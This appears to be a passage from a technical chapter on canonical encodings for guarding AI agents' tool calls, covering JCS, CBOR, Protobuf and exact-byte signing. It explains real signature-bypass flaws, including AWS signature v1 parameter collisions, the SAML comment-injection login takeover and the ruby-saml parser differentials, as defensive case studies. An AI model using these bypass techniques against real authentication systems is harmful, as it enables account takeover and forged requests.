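The guard also needs a token's network and address to find the right record, because several tokens can share a name. Bitquery's *LOBSTAR (Lobstar Wilde) Token on Solana* describes a token with a total market value of about $3,560. Another Bitquery page with the same title describes a different token at another address that last traded at about 13 cents. Cyberscope lists a token called Lobstar with six decimals, as Branch's explanation requires, but the shared name does not establish that this is the token Lobstar Wilde sent.

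On Ethereum-type networks, a token's own program usually reports the token's number of decimals, and a dishonest developer can write a program that later reports a different number. Using a reviewed copy of the number is safer there than looking it up for every request.

### Times, percentages and storage sizes

A time without a time zone can refer to several moments. In Berlin, clocks go back from 3:00 to 2:00 on 25 October 2026, so 2:30 happens twice that night. If an agent asks to delete backups made before `2026-10-25T02:30:00`, the guard and the executor can choose cut-offs an hour apart. Adding the difference from Coordinated Universal Time (UTC), the international reference time, removes the ambiguity:

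```
2026-10-25T02:30:00+02:00   =   2026-10-25T00:30:00Z
2026-10-25T02:30:00+01:00   =   2026-10-25T01:30:00Z
```

The Z at the end of a timestamp means UTC, and normalisation can convert every past time to this form. Time zone abbreviations are unsafe because IST, for example, can mean Indian, Irish or Israeli time. A future appointment needs the local time and a named zone such as `Europe/Berlin`, because a government may change its clock rules before that date.

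Daily spending caps depend on time zones too. A payment at 00:30 on 2 March in Berlin is at 23:30 on 1 March in UTC. If the guard counts days in UTC and the policy's author meant Berlin time, the payment counts towards the wrong day's total.

Software often stores a time as the number of seconds or milliseconds since the start of 1970, depending on the language. If the sender writes an approval's expiry time in milliseconds and the guard reads it as seconds, an approval meant to last an hour remains valid until about the year 58,700. A range check works well here because the guard can refuse any expiry more than a day away.

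Percentage errors usually come from confusing 15 with 0.15 for a discount of 15%. A field for fractions, limited to values from 0 to 1, rejects 15. A field for percentages, limited to values from 0 to 100, accepts 0.15 and applies a discount of only 0.15%. Both accept 1, which means 100% in the first field and 1% in the second. A name such as `discount_percent` makes the meaning clear. Financial software often uses whole basis points (hundredths of a percent), so 15% becomes 1500 and needs no decimal point.

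Storage sizes have two sets of units that people often confuse. A gigabyte (GB) is 10^9 bytes, while a gibibyte (GiB) is 2^30, or 1,073,741,824. Some programs label gibibytes as GB. If a guard approves 500 GB and the executor allocates 500 GiB, the agent gets about 37 GB more than the guard allowed. The error is only 7%, so almost no range check would catch it.

Unit abbreviations can also be misread. In UCUM, the code for a byte is `By`, because `B` stands for the bel, a unit used for sound levels. Kubernetes, a system for running software on many computers, uses `M` for a million and `m` for a thousandth, so `400m` of memory means 0.4 bytes. A field called `size_bytes` that accepts only whole numbers avoids both problems.

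## RFC 8785: one byte string for each JSON value

There are many ways to write the same request as JSON, even when its fields are valid and its units are clear. The JSON Canonicalization Scheme (JCS), which Rundgren, Jordan and Erdtman published as *RFC 8785* in June 2020, turns each JSON value into a single byte string that programs can hash or sign. RFC 8785 is an informational document, not an internet standard, and the RFC Editor takes no position on its value in the opening notice. Even so, several recent proposals for agent systems depend on it.

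The alternative to canonicalisation is to sign the exact bytes the sender transmits, usually encoded as base64url text. Rundgren and colleagues wanted a signed object to remain ordinary JSON, which is easier to log and document.

### From JSON value to canonical bytes

JCS requires its input to be I-JSON, the restricted version of JSON described earlier. Field names must not repeat within an object, strings must be valid Unicode, and every number must fit the 64-bit floating-point format. JCS has no rule for choosing between two values of a repeated field, so a strict parser has to reject such a request before JCS runs.

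The serialiser writes no white space outside strings, but it keeps spaces inside them. In strings, it escapes only the characters that JSON does not allow in raw form. It puts a backslash before each quotation mark or backslash. It writes control characters, such as tabs and line breaks, as a short escape like `\n` if JSON has one, and otherwise as `\u` with four lower-case hexadecimal digits. Every other character appears as itself, so `\u20ac` in the input becomes €.

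The serialiser formats numbers by the rules of ECMAScript, the standard behind JavaScript. It writes the fewest digits that a parser would read back as the same floating-point value, so `4.50` becomes `4.5` and `333333333.33333329` becomes `333333333.3333333`. It uses an exponent for numbers of 10^21 and above, as in `1e+21`, and for numbers closer to zero than 10^-6, as in `1e-7`.

JCS therefore gives the earlier account numbers 9007199254740992 and 9007199254740993 the same bytes, so an approval for one account would also cover the other. RFC 8785 requires applications to write such numbers as strings.

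Next, JCS sorts the names in each object by their UTF-16 code units. UTF-16 represents text as 16-bit numbers, and strings in JavaScript, Java and .NET use it internally. Most characters take one unit, but those numbered above U+FFFF, including most emoji, take two, called a surrogate pair. JCS decodes any escapes in the names before comparing them unit by unit, and it ignores the alphabetical rules of particular languages. If one name is the beginning of another, the shorter one comes first. JCS also sorts the names in objects nested inside other objects or lists, but it keeps the order of a list's items because that order may carry meaning.

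Finally, the program encodes the result in UTF-8. A euro sign becomes the three bytes `e2 82 ac`, and each English letter or digit becomes one byte.

### The payment request in canonical bytes

Here are two requests for the running example's payment, with different field orders, spacing and spellings:

```
{"tool":"pay_supplier","arguments":{"supplier":"S-204","amount":1250.50,"currency":"EUR"}}

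{ "arguments": { "currency": "EUR", "amount": 1.2505e3, "supplier": "S-\u003204" },
  "tool": "pay_supplier" }
```

After parsing and the conversion to cents shown earlier, the two objects hold the same values in different orders. JCS puts `arguments` before `tool` and sorts the arguments as `amount_cents`, `currency` and `supplier`. Both requests give this line:

```
{"arguments":{"amount_cents":125050,"currency":"EUR","supplier":"S-204"},"tool":"pay_supplier"}
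```

In hexadecimal, its 95 bytes are:

```
7b 22 61 72 67 75 6d 65 6e 74 73 22 3a 7b 22 61 6d 6f 75 6e
74 5f 63 65 6e 74 73 22 3a 31 32 35 30 35 30 2c 22 63 75 72
72 65 6e 63 79 22 3a 22 45 55 52 22 2c 22 73 75 70 70 6c 69
65 72 22 3a 22 53 2d 32 30 34 22 7d 2c 22 74 6f 6f 6c 22 3a
22 70 61 79 5f 73 75 70 70 6c 69 65 72 22 7d
```

Any correct SHA-256 implementation computes the same digest from these bytes. The bytes are also valid JSON, so the guard can send them to the executor in place of the agent's text. The executor can check that they are still in canonical form by parsing them, serialising the result with JCS and comparing the output with the bytes it received.

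JCS would have matched these two requests even without the conversion to cents, because both amounts parse to the same number, which JCS writes as `1250.5`. If the tool took amounts as strings, JCS would not have matched them.

### Differences that JCS keeps

JCS serialises each value according to its JSON type, without accounting for what a tool does with the field. It produces different bytes for the two requests in every pair in this table, although many tools would treat them as equivalent.

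| First request | Second request | Schema rule that would match them |
|---|---|---|
| `"amount":"1250.5"` | `"amount":"1250.50"` | Require exactly two decimals |
| No `urgent` field | `"urgent":null` | Refuse null, or remove it |
| No `urgent` field | `"urgent":false`, the default | Fill in the default |
| `é` as one character | `e` followed by a combining accent | Require one Unicode form |
| `"regions":["EU","UK"]` | `"regions":["UK","EU"]` | Sort the list if its order has no meaning |

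Confusing an absent field with a null one can make a genuine signature fail verification. *Signed Decision Receipts for Machine-to-Machine Access Control* (Farley, 2026) proposes a format for signed records of a guard's decisions. The signature is in the same object as the data it covers, so a verifier has to remove it before computing the digest. Farley requires verifiers to delete the field. If a verifier set it to null instead, it would hash different bytes and reject a valid receipt.

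Unicode has two ways to write many accented letters. The letter é can be the single character U+00E9, encoded in UTF-8 as `c3 a9`, or a plain `e` followed by the combining accent U+0301, encoded together as `65 cc 81`. The two forms look identical on screen. Unicode defines normalisation forms that convert one into the other, but JCS requires programs to leave strings unchanged.

This is a sensible choice for a general scheme because on some file systems the two spellings of `café.txt` name different files. If JCS merged them, an approval to delete one file would also cover the other. On other systems the spellings name the same file, and a tool's owner may want them to match. The owner has to decide for each field whether to treat them as the same, and the schema should state which form the field accepts.

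A parser can also change strings before JCS processes them, because some parsers convert text that looks like a date or a large integer into a native type as they read. RFC 8785 gives the example of an object that contains the time `"2019-01-28T07:45:10Z"` and the integer `"055"`, both as strings. If a parser converts them, they are serialised as `"2019-01-28T07:45:10.000Z"` and `"55"`, which changes the digest. The RFC requires programs to keep such values as strings for serialisation and to convert them in a later step.

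### Schema rules in an x402 draft

*JCS Canonicalisation Discipline for Agentic-Payment Receipts* (Hopley, 2026) sets out rules to apply before JCS. Hopley wrote them for receipts from agent payments, including x402 payments. The document is an individual Internet-Draft, not a standard. Anyone may submit such a draft, and it expires after six months. Hopley states that no Internet Engineering Task Force working group has reviewed the document and that he alone controls changes to it.

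His rules cover these points:

- A point in time is an integer number of milliseconds since the start of 1970, never a text such as `2026-05-28T12:00:00Z`, because the same instant could also appear with `+00:00` or in another time zone.
- Field names are fixed. If a system accepts `tx_id` as another name for `transaction_id`, it has to convert the name before hashing.
- The schema specifies the order of a list wherever only one order should count.
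- Amounts should be strings of digits in the smallest unit.
- The verifier rejects wrong types, missing required fields and repeated names. It also rejects text in the wrong Unicode form if the schema requires a particular one.
- A field called `canon_version` names the version of the rules, and the digest covers this field too.

The last rule is for records that firms must keep for years. An auditor can read the version from the receipt itself and apply the rules in force when it was issued.

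Hopley requires verifiers to reject invalid values rather than convert them. Verifiers might convert the same value differently, and an auditor who later hashes the stored original would get a different digest from that of the converted value. This rule is stricter than the running example, in which the guard converts euros to cents. The guard avoids these problems if it stores and signs the converted request, because later checks then start from the same bytes.

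Requiring times to be integers does not prevent confusion between seconds and milliseconds, although Hopley's field name, `timestamp_ms`, helps. The draft also has no rule for whether an optional field should be omitted, set to null or written with its default value, so two systems can follow it exactly and still produce different digests for equivalent receipts. A guard that adopts these rules would also need one for optional fields.

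Hopley also describes an identifier for an agent's action, called `action_ref`. It is the SHA-256 digest of a canonical object whose four fields are the agent's identifier, the type of action, its scope and the time in milliseconds. Hopley gives a worked example with its digest, which developers can try to reproduce when testing a new library. The identifier stays the same as a payment moves from authorisation to settlement or refund, so it can link the records of each stage. However, it would be a poor basis for an approval because it leaves out the payee and the amount. Two different refunds that an agent declares in the same millisecond would have the same `action_ref`.

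Farley also uses the name `action_ref`, but for a digest of `agentId`, `actionType`, `scopeRequired` and `timestamp`, meant to let two separate guards recognise the same action. Although both drafts use JCS and SHA-256, their digests of the same action will not match, because the field names are part of the hashed bytes.

### Where implementations differ

Nora Foundation's textbook chapter *Canonicalization (RFC 8785 JCS)* lists four areas where JCS implementations tend to go wrong: the sort order of unusual characters, number formatting, lone surrogates, and special values such as negative zero. The chapter opens with a story about three organisations whose programs computed different digests, but it gives no source for the story and cites no specific bug reports. All four mistakes are easy to make under the rules in RFC 8785, though it is unclear how often they happen in practice.

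A common shortcut in Python is to use the standard JSON serialiser with sorted names and no spaces:

```
json.dumps(request, sort_keys=True, separators=(",", ":"))
```

This gives the correct bytes for the running example. It goes wrong on the following inputs.

| Input | RFC 8785 | Python shortcut |
|---|---|---|
| Two names: 😀 (U+1F600) and a Hebrew letter (U+FB33) | 😀 first | 😀 second |
| `1250.0` | `1250` | `1250.0` |
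| `0.00001` | `0.00001` | `1e-05` |
| `1e16` | `10000000000000000` | `1e+16` |
| `"\ud83d"`, half a surrogate pair | Error | `"\ud83d"` |
| `-0.0` | `0` | `-0.0` |

The first row differs because Python sorts by code point, the number that Unicode assigns to each character, and 1F600 is larger than FB33. JCS sorts by UTF-16 unit, and the emoji's first unit, D83D, is smaller than FB33. The two orders can differ only if a name contains a character above U+FFFF. Hopley's draft describes JCS as sorting by code point, so a developer who followed the draft instead of the RFC could put such names in the wrong order. Farley's draft uses both orders. It sorts one list of fields by their UTF-8 bytes, which gives code-point order, and uses JCS for the objects inside that list.

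Python switches to an exponent at 10^16 and JCS at 10^21. For small numbers, Python switches below 0.0001 and writes two digits in the exponent. The `1250.0` row matters most for payments, because a guard that used the shortcut on floating-point amounts would serialise every whole number of euros differently from a correct executor. Nora Foundation gives the exponent boundaries correctly but says that exponents have no plus sign, although the RFC's example contains `1e+30`.

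JCS requires an error when a string contains half a surrogate pair. A program that substitutes the standard replacement character instead can make two different file names equal, as Go's old JSON package did with invalid bytes. The RFC's sample JavaScript code doesn't raise this error and, according to its comments, leaves out error handling. The omission has a worse effect on numbers, because JavaScript reads `1e400` as infinity and writes infinity as `null`, so the sample code gives `{"amount":1e400}` and `{"amount":null}` the same canonical form. RFC 8785 requires an error here too.

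RFC 8785 originally specified only that JCS writes negative zero as `0`. If the guard hashes `0` but the executor parses the agent's text and gets −0, the executor could receive a value the digest doesn't cover. The difference rarely matters, but dividing by the value gives infinity in one case and negative infinity in the other. In May 2024 the RFC Editor published a verified correction under which a parser should raise an error when it reads `-0`.

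A strict schema prevents most of these problems. If all field names use plain English letters, every sort order gives the same result. Whole numbers within the safe range have the same digits in nearly every programming language if the program stores them as integers. The strict parser described earlier rejects unpaired surrogates and infinite numbers, and needs one more rule, for negative zero. Sort order remains a risk where the agent can choose field names, for instance when a tool accepts free-form labels.

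### Test vectors

A test vector is an input together with the exact output that a correct program must produce. Developers run the same vectors through every implementation and compare the results byte by byte. The vectors in RFC 8785 cover seven names to sort and about two dozen floating-point values, several of them next to the exponent boundaries. According to Nora Foundation, the main public collection has roughly 286,000 vectors. Rundgren and colleagues also suggest generating random numbers and comparing the output with that of V8, Google's widely used JavaScript engine.

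A simpler check is to serialise a value, parse the result and serialise it again. If the two outputs differ, the program is faulty. But a program that always sorts by code point passes this check, because it makes the same mistake both times. Finding that mistake requires comparing the program's output with external test vectors.

Test vectors should also cover inputs that a program must refuse. Farley's test suite, for example, includes a tampered proof that every verifier must reject. For a guard, useful cases would include a repeated name, half a surrogate pair and an infinite numeric value. Pairs of requests are useful too. For example, a request that omits a default value and one that includes it must give the same bytes after normalisation.

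Hopley reports that in May 2026, eight JCS libraries in eight programming languages produced identical bytes for each of 24 test vectors. He ran the test himself, on vectors from his own company. He describes the libraries as the work of separate authors, but his table lists Samuel Erdtman, a co-author of the RFC, for both the TypeScript and the Java library. The vectors came from action identifiers and payment receipts, which probably contain mostly plain text and whole numbers. The test is therefore good evidence that the libraries agree on ordinary receipts, but weaker evidence that they agree on numbers near 10^21 or emoji in field names.

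### AegisAgent's variant

The AegisAgent system ties a person's approval to the digest of one exact action. Its Python, Go and TypeScript client libraries and its Rust gateway must all compute the same digest, or the system will block an action that the person approved. AegisAgent's *ADR-0003* (2026), a record of a design decision, explains why the developers didn't simply use RFC 8785. They believed that the available libraries still differed in small ways, such as how they format unusual numbers, so they defined their own scheme, `aegis-jcs-1`.

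The scheme sorts names by code point instead of by UTF-16 code unit. The record gives no separate reason for this, but it was probably easier, because Python, Go and Rust already sort strings this way and only TypeScript needs extra code. The scheme also writes null when an action has no resource, so that field is never left out. It rejects NaN and infinity, as the RFC does. It also requires text to appear as raw UTF-8, never as `\u` escapes. This rule presumably applies only to characters such as é, since JSON has no other way to write some control characters.

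The developers' complaint seems to be more about libraries than about the RFC, which specifies the output for every number by reference to ECMAScript. They give no example of two libraries that disagree. Their four new serialisers could also contain the same mistakes. AegisAgent's protection comes from the shared test vectors that all four implementations must pass whenever the code changes. The developers could have run the same tests on four existing RFC 8785 libraries.

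Because of this choice, anyone who adds support for another language must reproduce the scheme exactly, and an outside auditor with an ordinary JCS library can get a different digest for some actions. But the developers control the rules and have promised to publish any change as `aegis-jcs-2`, so that old approvals can still be verified.

AegisAgent also records two alternatives that the developers rejected. Hashing the agent's text as sent would have been simplest, but an approval would have become invalid if a proxy reordered the fields. A binary format would have been as exact as JSON, but harder for people to read when finding out why an approval failed.

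### Deterministic CBOR and Protocol Buffers

The binary format that AegisAgent's developers considered was CBOR, an internet standard for data structures much like those of JSON. Ordinary CBOR also allows several encodings of the same value. The amount 125050 takes five bytes in its shortest form, but a program may also write it in nine:

```
1a 00 01 e8 7a
1b 00 00 00 00 00 01 e8 7a
```

The deterministic subset of CBOR defined in RFC 8949 requires the shortest form for every number, puts the length of each list or object at its start, and sorts field names by their encoded bytes. Unlike JCS, it can represent integers above 2^53 exactly, so the two account numbers from before would have different encodings.

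CBOR has had trouble with sort order too. ImperialViolet (2022) recounts that developers interpreted the canonical order in the previous version of the standard differently. Some read it as sorting by length and then by bytes, while the protocol for security keys sorts by type first. RFC 8949 replaced this order with a plain comparison of the encoded bytes, but it still describes the older length-first order as an option. Comparing bytes puts the key 100, encoded as `18 64`, before −1, encoded as `20`, and the length-first order reverses them. Docs.rs' *cbor2 1.0.3*, the documentation of a Rust library, uses this pair as its example but swaps the two results.

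RFC 8949 also leaves some decisions to each application, which makes it harder for a general library to offer deterministic encoding as a simple option. *CBOR Common Deterministic Encoding (CDE)* (Bormann, 2025), a working-group draft, proposes a common set of choices.

CBOR has one clear advantage in the evidence behind it. Ramananandro, Ebner and colleagues (2025), in *Secure Parsing and Serializing with Separation Logic*, give what they describe as the first proof that deterministic CBOR has exactly one encoding for each value. If p is the parser and b1 and b2 are complete encodings, they prove that

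p(b1) = p(b2) implies b1 = b2, whenever p accepts both.

They also provide a library in C and Rust with a machine-checked proof that it follows this definition. A guard that uses such a parser can hash the received bytes directly, because the parser rejects every other encoding. The proof covers only this library. It also does not show that a missing field equals its default, so CBOR needs the schema rules as much as JSON does.

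Protocol Buffers, Google's binary message format, is a poor choice for digests. Protobuf's *Proto Serialization Is Not Canonical* explains that the same message can produce different bytes after a change to the schema, application, build settings or library version. The libraries have a deterministic mode, but its output is not canonical either. Google's developers deliberately leave field order undefined so they can make the software faster, and in some configurations they scramble it to stop programmers from relying on it.

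Undeclared fields cause a deeper problem. When a program with an old schema receives a message with a newer field, the library keeps the field's bytes to pass them on. The format marks raw bytes and nested messages in the same way, so the library cannot determine whether an undeclared field contains a message whose fields it should sort or data that it must leave alone.

Some projects restrict the format instead of abandoning it. The Cosmos blockchain project's *ADR 027* (2020) notes that a message has a practically unlimited number of valid encodings and defines a deterministic subset for signing. Protobuf's documentation recommends that programmers write their own digest function for each message type and name every field in it. A guard that does this must also refuse undeclared fields, because the digest would not cover them and the executor might still act on them.

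## Canonical forms that failed: Amazon's request signatures and SAML logins

RFC 8785 and deterministic CBOR give each value one byte string, but a system that relies on a canonical form can still fail. The canonicalisation rules may give two different requests the same bytes, as Amazon's early request signatures did. Software may also check the canonical text and then act on the original, as many SAML login systems did. Because of such flaws, some engineers argue that software should sign the exact bytes it sends, without canonicalising them.

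### Amazon's missing separators

Customers of Amazon Web Services (AWS) manage databases and servers by sending web requests, and they sign each request with a secret key. The signature is an HMAC, a digest computed from both the text and the key, so only someone with the key can produce it. In December 2008 Colin Percival, who ran a backup service on AWS, published a flaw in version 1 of this scheme on his blog, Daemonology. According to his post, *AWS signature version 1 is insecure*, the program splits the request into parameter names and values, sorts the pairs by name, joins everything into one string and computes the HMAC of that string.

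Sorting gives the same string whatever order the parameters arrive in, as a canonical form should. But the third step puts nothing between the names and the values, so `foo=bar` and `foob=ar` both become `foobar`. Take a made-up printing service that prints a whole document unless the request limits the number of pages:

```
label=draft&pages=2   ->  labeldraftpages2
label=draftpages2     ->  labeldraftpages2
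```

The first request prints two pages with the label "draft". The second prints every page with the label "draftpages2". The HMAC worked correctly, but a signature on either request is valid for both because they have the same canonical bytes. This breaks the condition that requests with different effects must have different canonical bytes.

Percival's example was a website that lets users tag documents and stores the tags in an Amazon database. The website signs each request, but the user chooses the text of the tag. An attacker could submit a tag whose text spelled out further parameters. The website would sign the request to store that tag, and the same signature would also be valid for a request in which the text became real parameters and made the attacker the document's owner. The attacker had to capture the signature on its way to Amazon, so Percival advised affected customers to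 use encrypted connections or move to version 2. An AI agent's host is in much the same position if it signs requests containing text from strangers.

Percival reported the flaw on 1 May 2008, and Amazon released version 2 seven and a half months later. Its staff found that the flaw also affected two services he had not examined. They let him review the new design and later test his own code against it. The test exposed an ambiguity in the documentation, though he had reviewed the method and seen no problem with it.

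Laughing Meme's *Enigma rotors* (2008) mentions a similar problem in early drafts of OAuth, a standard for giving one service limited access to an account on another. Latacora's *How (not) to sign a JSON object* (2019), an essay by a security consultancy, describes the same mistake at the photo site Flickr, which also used a weaker keyed digest. With that digest, an attacker could add text to the end of a signed message and compute a valid signature without the key. In Latacora's example, the attacker adds `role=admin` to the end of a message that already contains `role=user`, and a program that keeps the last value makes the user an administrator. A strict parser would refuse this message because `role` occurs twice.

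### Delimiters and length prefixes

Version 2 kept the separators in the signed string. Separators work only if they can't also appear as ordinary characters inside a name or value. Percent-encoding ensures this in web requests by writing `&` inside a value as `%26` and `=` as `%3D`. It also writes `%` as `%25`, because otherwise the value `&` would have the same encoding as the literal text `%26`.

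Length prefixes need no escaping. The program writes the number of bytes in each piece, then a colon, then the piece:

```
label=draft&pages=2   ->  5:label5:draft5:pages1:2
label=draftpages2     ->  5:label11:draftpages2
```

A decoder reads digits up to the first colon, takes that many bytes and starts again. A digit or colon inside a value cannot mislead it, because it has already counted the value's bytes. Write e for the encoder and d for the decoder. Since d(e(x)) = x for every list of strings x,

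e(x) = e(y) implies x = d(e(x)) = d(e(y)) = y.

Two different lists therefore never have the same encoding. This is true of any encoding that a decoder can reverse, including canonical JSON, where quotation marks and backslashes serve the same purpose as the separators.

A guard can still repeat Amazon's mistake if it builds a request identity by joining fields itself. Suppose it hashes the supplier number followed directly by the amount in cents:

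```
S-204, 1,250.50 euros    ->  S-204125050
S-20,  41,250.50 euros   ->  S-204125050
```

A person's approval of the first payment would also cover the second, which is 33 times as large and goes to a different supplier. Length prefixes would prevent this collision by making the two strings `5:S-2046:125050` and `4:S-207:4125050`. Hashing the whole canonical JSON object would also prevent it.

### A comment inside a user's name

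SAML (Security Assertion Markup Language) lets people use one login for many websites. An identity provider, such as a company's login server, checks who the user is and signs an XML document that names them. The user's browser carries the document to the website, which verifies the signature and logs in the named user. The user can edit the document on the way, so the website depends on the signature to detect changes.

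The same XML document can be written in many ways, so the signer and the verifier both canonicalise it before computing the digest. The most common method puts attributes in a fixed order and removes comments (text between `<!--` and `-->`).

On 27 February 2018 Duo Security, a maker of login software, disclosed a flaw in how websites read the document after this step. Kelby Ludwig, one of its engineers, told The CyberWire that he had come across it during an internal review of a potential dependency. Duo Security's *Duo Finds SAML Vulnerabilities Affecting Multiple Implementations* shows the cause with this element:

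```
<NameID>klud<!-- a comment? -->wig</NameID>
```

An XML parser may split it into the text `klud`, a comment and the text `wig`. When a program reads the element's text, Python's lxml library returns only `klud`, while ElementTree, another Python library, returns `kludwig`. Ludwig considered lxml's behaviour technically correct, though not what most programmers would expect.

An attacker with the account `user@user.com.evil.com` could log in normally, then insert an empty comment after `user@user.com` in the signed document:

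| Stage | Name |
|---|---|
| The identity provider signs the document | `user@user.com.evil.com` |
| The website removes the comment and verifies the signature | `user@user.com.evil.com` |
| The website reads the original document and logs the user in | `user@user.com` |

The attacker did not need the other user's password or anyone's signing key. Duo listed six affected products, including its own gateway. The risk was greater for websites where anyone could register an account with the identity provider, and smaller where the website accepted only email addresses from approved domains or asked for a second form of identification itself.

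If comments have no meaning, the canonical form was correct to give the same bytes to documents that differed only in a comment. The fault was that the website went back to the original document after canonicalisation. If the canonical form were instead at fault for merging two documents that lxml users would read differently, its correctness would depend on the behaviour of every library that might read the document later.

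*Canonical XML Version 1.0* (Boyer, 2001) states that two documents with the same canonical form are logically equivalent, apart from a few unusual cases. Equivalent documents can still have different canonical forms, because applications have their own rules of equivalence that no general XML standard can include. A guard that uses canonical XML to detect duplicates could therefore miss some, even if every program read the canonical text.

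Duo suggested several repairs. Library developers could collect all the text around a comment, which fixes this particular difference. The two sides could use a canonical form that keeps comments, so that an inserted comment invalidates the signature, but both would have to support it, and an attacker must not be able to change which canonicalisation method the document specifies. Or the library could take the user's name from the canonicalised document after verifying the signature. This last repair is the best of the three because it also protects against differences that nobody has found yet. SSOReady, a vendor of login software, likewise quotes a rule that a program should work on the transformed and signed data instead of the original.

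### Earlier and later cases

Amazon had a related problem in 2011, more than six years before Duo's disclosure. Some of its services accepted signed requests in SOAP, an XML format. AWS's *Reported SOAP Request Parsing Vulnerabilities* (2011) acknowledges that parsing errors may have let through specially crafted requests with duplicate elements or missing signatures, and states that no customers were affected. The Register (2011) attributes the weakness to Amazon's interface verifying signatures and interpreting XML separately. The researchers who found the weakness, from Ruhr University in Germany, found that Eucalyptus, open-source software for private clouds, was similarly vulnerable.

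The problem returned in ruby-saml, one of the six products on Duo's list. Two advisories from March 2025, CVE-2025-25291 and CVE-2025-25292, describe new ways to bypass its signature check. The library used two XML parsers during verification, and an attacker could write a document that the parsers interpreted differently. The 2018 repair had dealt with comments but, as with CouchDB, left other differences between parsers in place.

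### Signing the bytes as sent

Latacora calls canonicalisation a "quagnet", a blend of "quagmire" and "vulnerability magnet". It advises the sender to serialise a message in any convenient way, compute an HMAC over the exact bytes and attach the result outside the message. The receiver verifies those bytes before parsing them, and parses nothing else. The two sides need not agree on sort order, number formats or the treatment of comments, and someone without the key cannot get any text to the message parser.

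JSON Web Signature (JWS), a format common in login tokens, follows this approach. The sender encodes a header and the message as base64url text, which contains only letters, digits, hyphens and underscores, and signs that text. Jones notes in the specification that the message can be any content, not just JSON. The example message is JSON with line breaks between its fields, and the encoding preserves those line breaks.

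The developers of JWS had XML's problems in mind. Barnes (2014), in *Use Cases and Requirements for JSON Object Signing and Encryption (JOSE)*, names XML canonicalisation as an example of the complexity that made a simpler JSON format desirable. W3C, which published the XML signature standard, also lists complex canonicalisation methods, and support for arbitrary ones, as a source of problems. In a mailing-list debate, Waite (2021), in *Re: VC-JWT perma-thread*, describes JWS and its related formats as a "sealed envelope", whose contents reach the application byte for byte as the sender signed them. He warns that with canonicalisation, a developer must process the data in the same way as the security software or risk a vulnerability; Duo's case is an example of that risk.

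The Dead Simple Signing Envelope (DSSE) applies the same idea to records of how people built a piece of software. Krishna, in *in-toto*, describes a 2022 project to move one such record system to DSSE because its old format required canonicalisation, "which should be avoided for security reasons". DSSE signs the message's type and length along with the message, according to Nora Foundation's *Digital Signatures (Ed25519)*. For the running example's 95 canonical bytes, the signed string would begin like this:

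```
DSSEv1 16 application/json 95 {"arguments":{"amount_cents":125050,
```

The numbers 16 and 95 are length prefixes, which stop text from moving between the type and the message. The type prevents someone from presenting a signature on one kind of message as a signature on another. A guard would need more specific types than `application/json`, perhaps one for approvals and another for log entries. Otherwise a signed log entry for a refused payment might pass as an approval.

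Verifying a signature before parsing the message protects an agent system less than it protects an ordinary service. If the host signs whatever the model writes, it also signs any text the model copied from a malicious invoice. The signature shows that nobody changed the call after it left the host, but the receiver still needs a strict parser for the call. JWS also requires the receiver to parse the header before verifying the signature, which Latacora considers a weakness.

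An envelope also causes practical problems, because intermediate programs may need to read the message as ordinary JSON. Latacora suggests leaving the object readable and adding a field that contains the exact string the sender signed. This roughly doubles the message's size, and the receiver must verify the signed string and then compare it with the visible object. If a guard skipped that comparison and evaluated the visible object while the executor ran the signed string, the system would again have two versions of one request.

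### Two spellings, two identities

Signing the exact bytes doesn't help software recognise a repeated request. A host could validly sign each of the three spellings of the running example's payment, and a duplicate check based on the signed bytes would let the executor pay three times.

Latacora acknowledges that equivalent requests have different representations under this approach, but considers this unimportant in most cases, including authenticating requests to a service. That is reasonable for authentication, where the receiver only has to check whether the sender holds the key. But to enforce a spending limit or detect duplicates, the system must determine whether it has already counted or made the payment, and a signature on the new request cannot establish that.

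In the mailing-list debate, Orie Steele similarly objected that a sender can produce a new signature for every possible order of an object's fields, so a system may store huge numbers of objects with the same content. Waite (2021) replied that an attacker would still have to send all that data, and could just as easily make a change that canonicalisation preserves, such as writing "José" with a different Unicode encoding. He therefore regarded removing such duplicates as an optimisation rather than a defence.

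Waite's argument is convincing for storage, where a copy takes up a little disk space. But a duplicate payment may cost 1,250.50 euros, and a timeout and a retry can cause one without any attacker. His point about attackers still applies. Someone who can steer the agent can change the invoice number as easily as the spelling, and the new request would have a new canonical form. To stop this, the guard has to compare the invoice number with the company's own records. A canonical form catches accidental respellings and those made by attackers who can alter only the spelling.

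Amazon eventually combined the two approaches. It replaced version 2 with version 4, which AWS says is the only version its S3 storage service accepts in regions opened after 30 January 2014. Latacora notes that version 4 covers the raw bytes of the request's body, so two bodies with the same fields in a different order have different signatures. Valsorda describes an HMAC over a canonicalised version of the HTTP request as a whole. This division makes sense because software between the sender and the receiver often rewrites web headers but usually leaves the body alone. The IETF draft *JWS/CT* (2022) combines the two approaches differently, by applying a JWS signature to an object's RFC 8785 form.

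A guard can also use both. It verifies the host's signature on the bytes it received, parses them strictly, and computes the request identity from the canonical form. It then signs the canonical bytes and sends them to the executor, which verifies them before parsing and reads nothing else. This gives the executor the protection Latacora recommends and gives all three spellings the same identity in the duplicate check.

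### Refusing input that is not canonical

A receiver can also require the sender to write the canonical form and refuse everything else. If p is the parser and c the function that writes canonical bytes, the receiver accepts b only when

c(p(b)) = b.

Suppose the receiver accepts two texts, b1 and b2, that encode equivalent requests. Then b1 = c(p(b1)) = c(p(b2)) = b2, so the texts are identical. The receiver can therefore use the digest of the received bytes as the request identity, and nobody has to choose between signing those bytes and signing a canonical form.

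The Distinguished Encoding Rules (DER), which website certificates use, make this possible for binary data. DER narrows a looser set of rules in which any non-zero byte can stand for "true". Under DER only `ff` can, so a strict decoder accepts `01 01 ff` and refuses `01 01 05`. It also refuses a length encoded in more bytes than necessary. But decoders are not always this strict. The certificate libraries that Barenghi and colleagues tested all accepted hundreds of thousands of certificates with invalid syntax. A decoder that accepts extra encodings no longer guarantees that each value has only one valid form.

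Ramananandro and colleagues warn that an attacker may be able to construct a second encoding of a signed CBOR object, which the application that signed it will not recognise as the same object. They cite research on Bitcoin, where third parties could once re-encode a signed payment and change its identifier without invalidating it. A company that searched for the old identifier might conclude that the payment had failed and send the money again.

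Their decoder avoids this by accepting only one encoding. It also rejects lists whose length is not given at the start, which ordinary CBOR allows so that data can be sent as a stream. A program reading such a stream might act on a valid beginning before an invalid end arrives, so the decoder validates the whole message before any program uses it.

A strict format is not enough if the schema has two ways to express the same thing. Ramananandro and colleagues built a tool that checks whether a CBOR schema is unambiguous, and they had to adapt the schemas of two published security standards before they could prove those schemas unambiguous. In the running example, the rule would have to specify whether a non-urgent payment must include `"urgent":false` or leave the field out, and the guard would reject the other version.

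### What the rule costs a language model

Here is how the three approaches treat the three spellings of the payment, if the agent sends each of them once:

| Approach | What the guard does | Amount paid |
|---|---|---|
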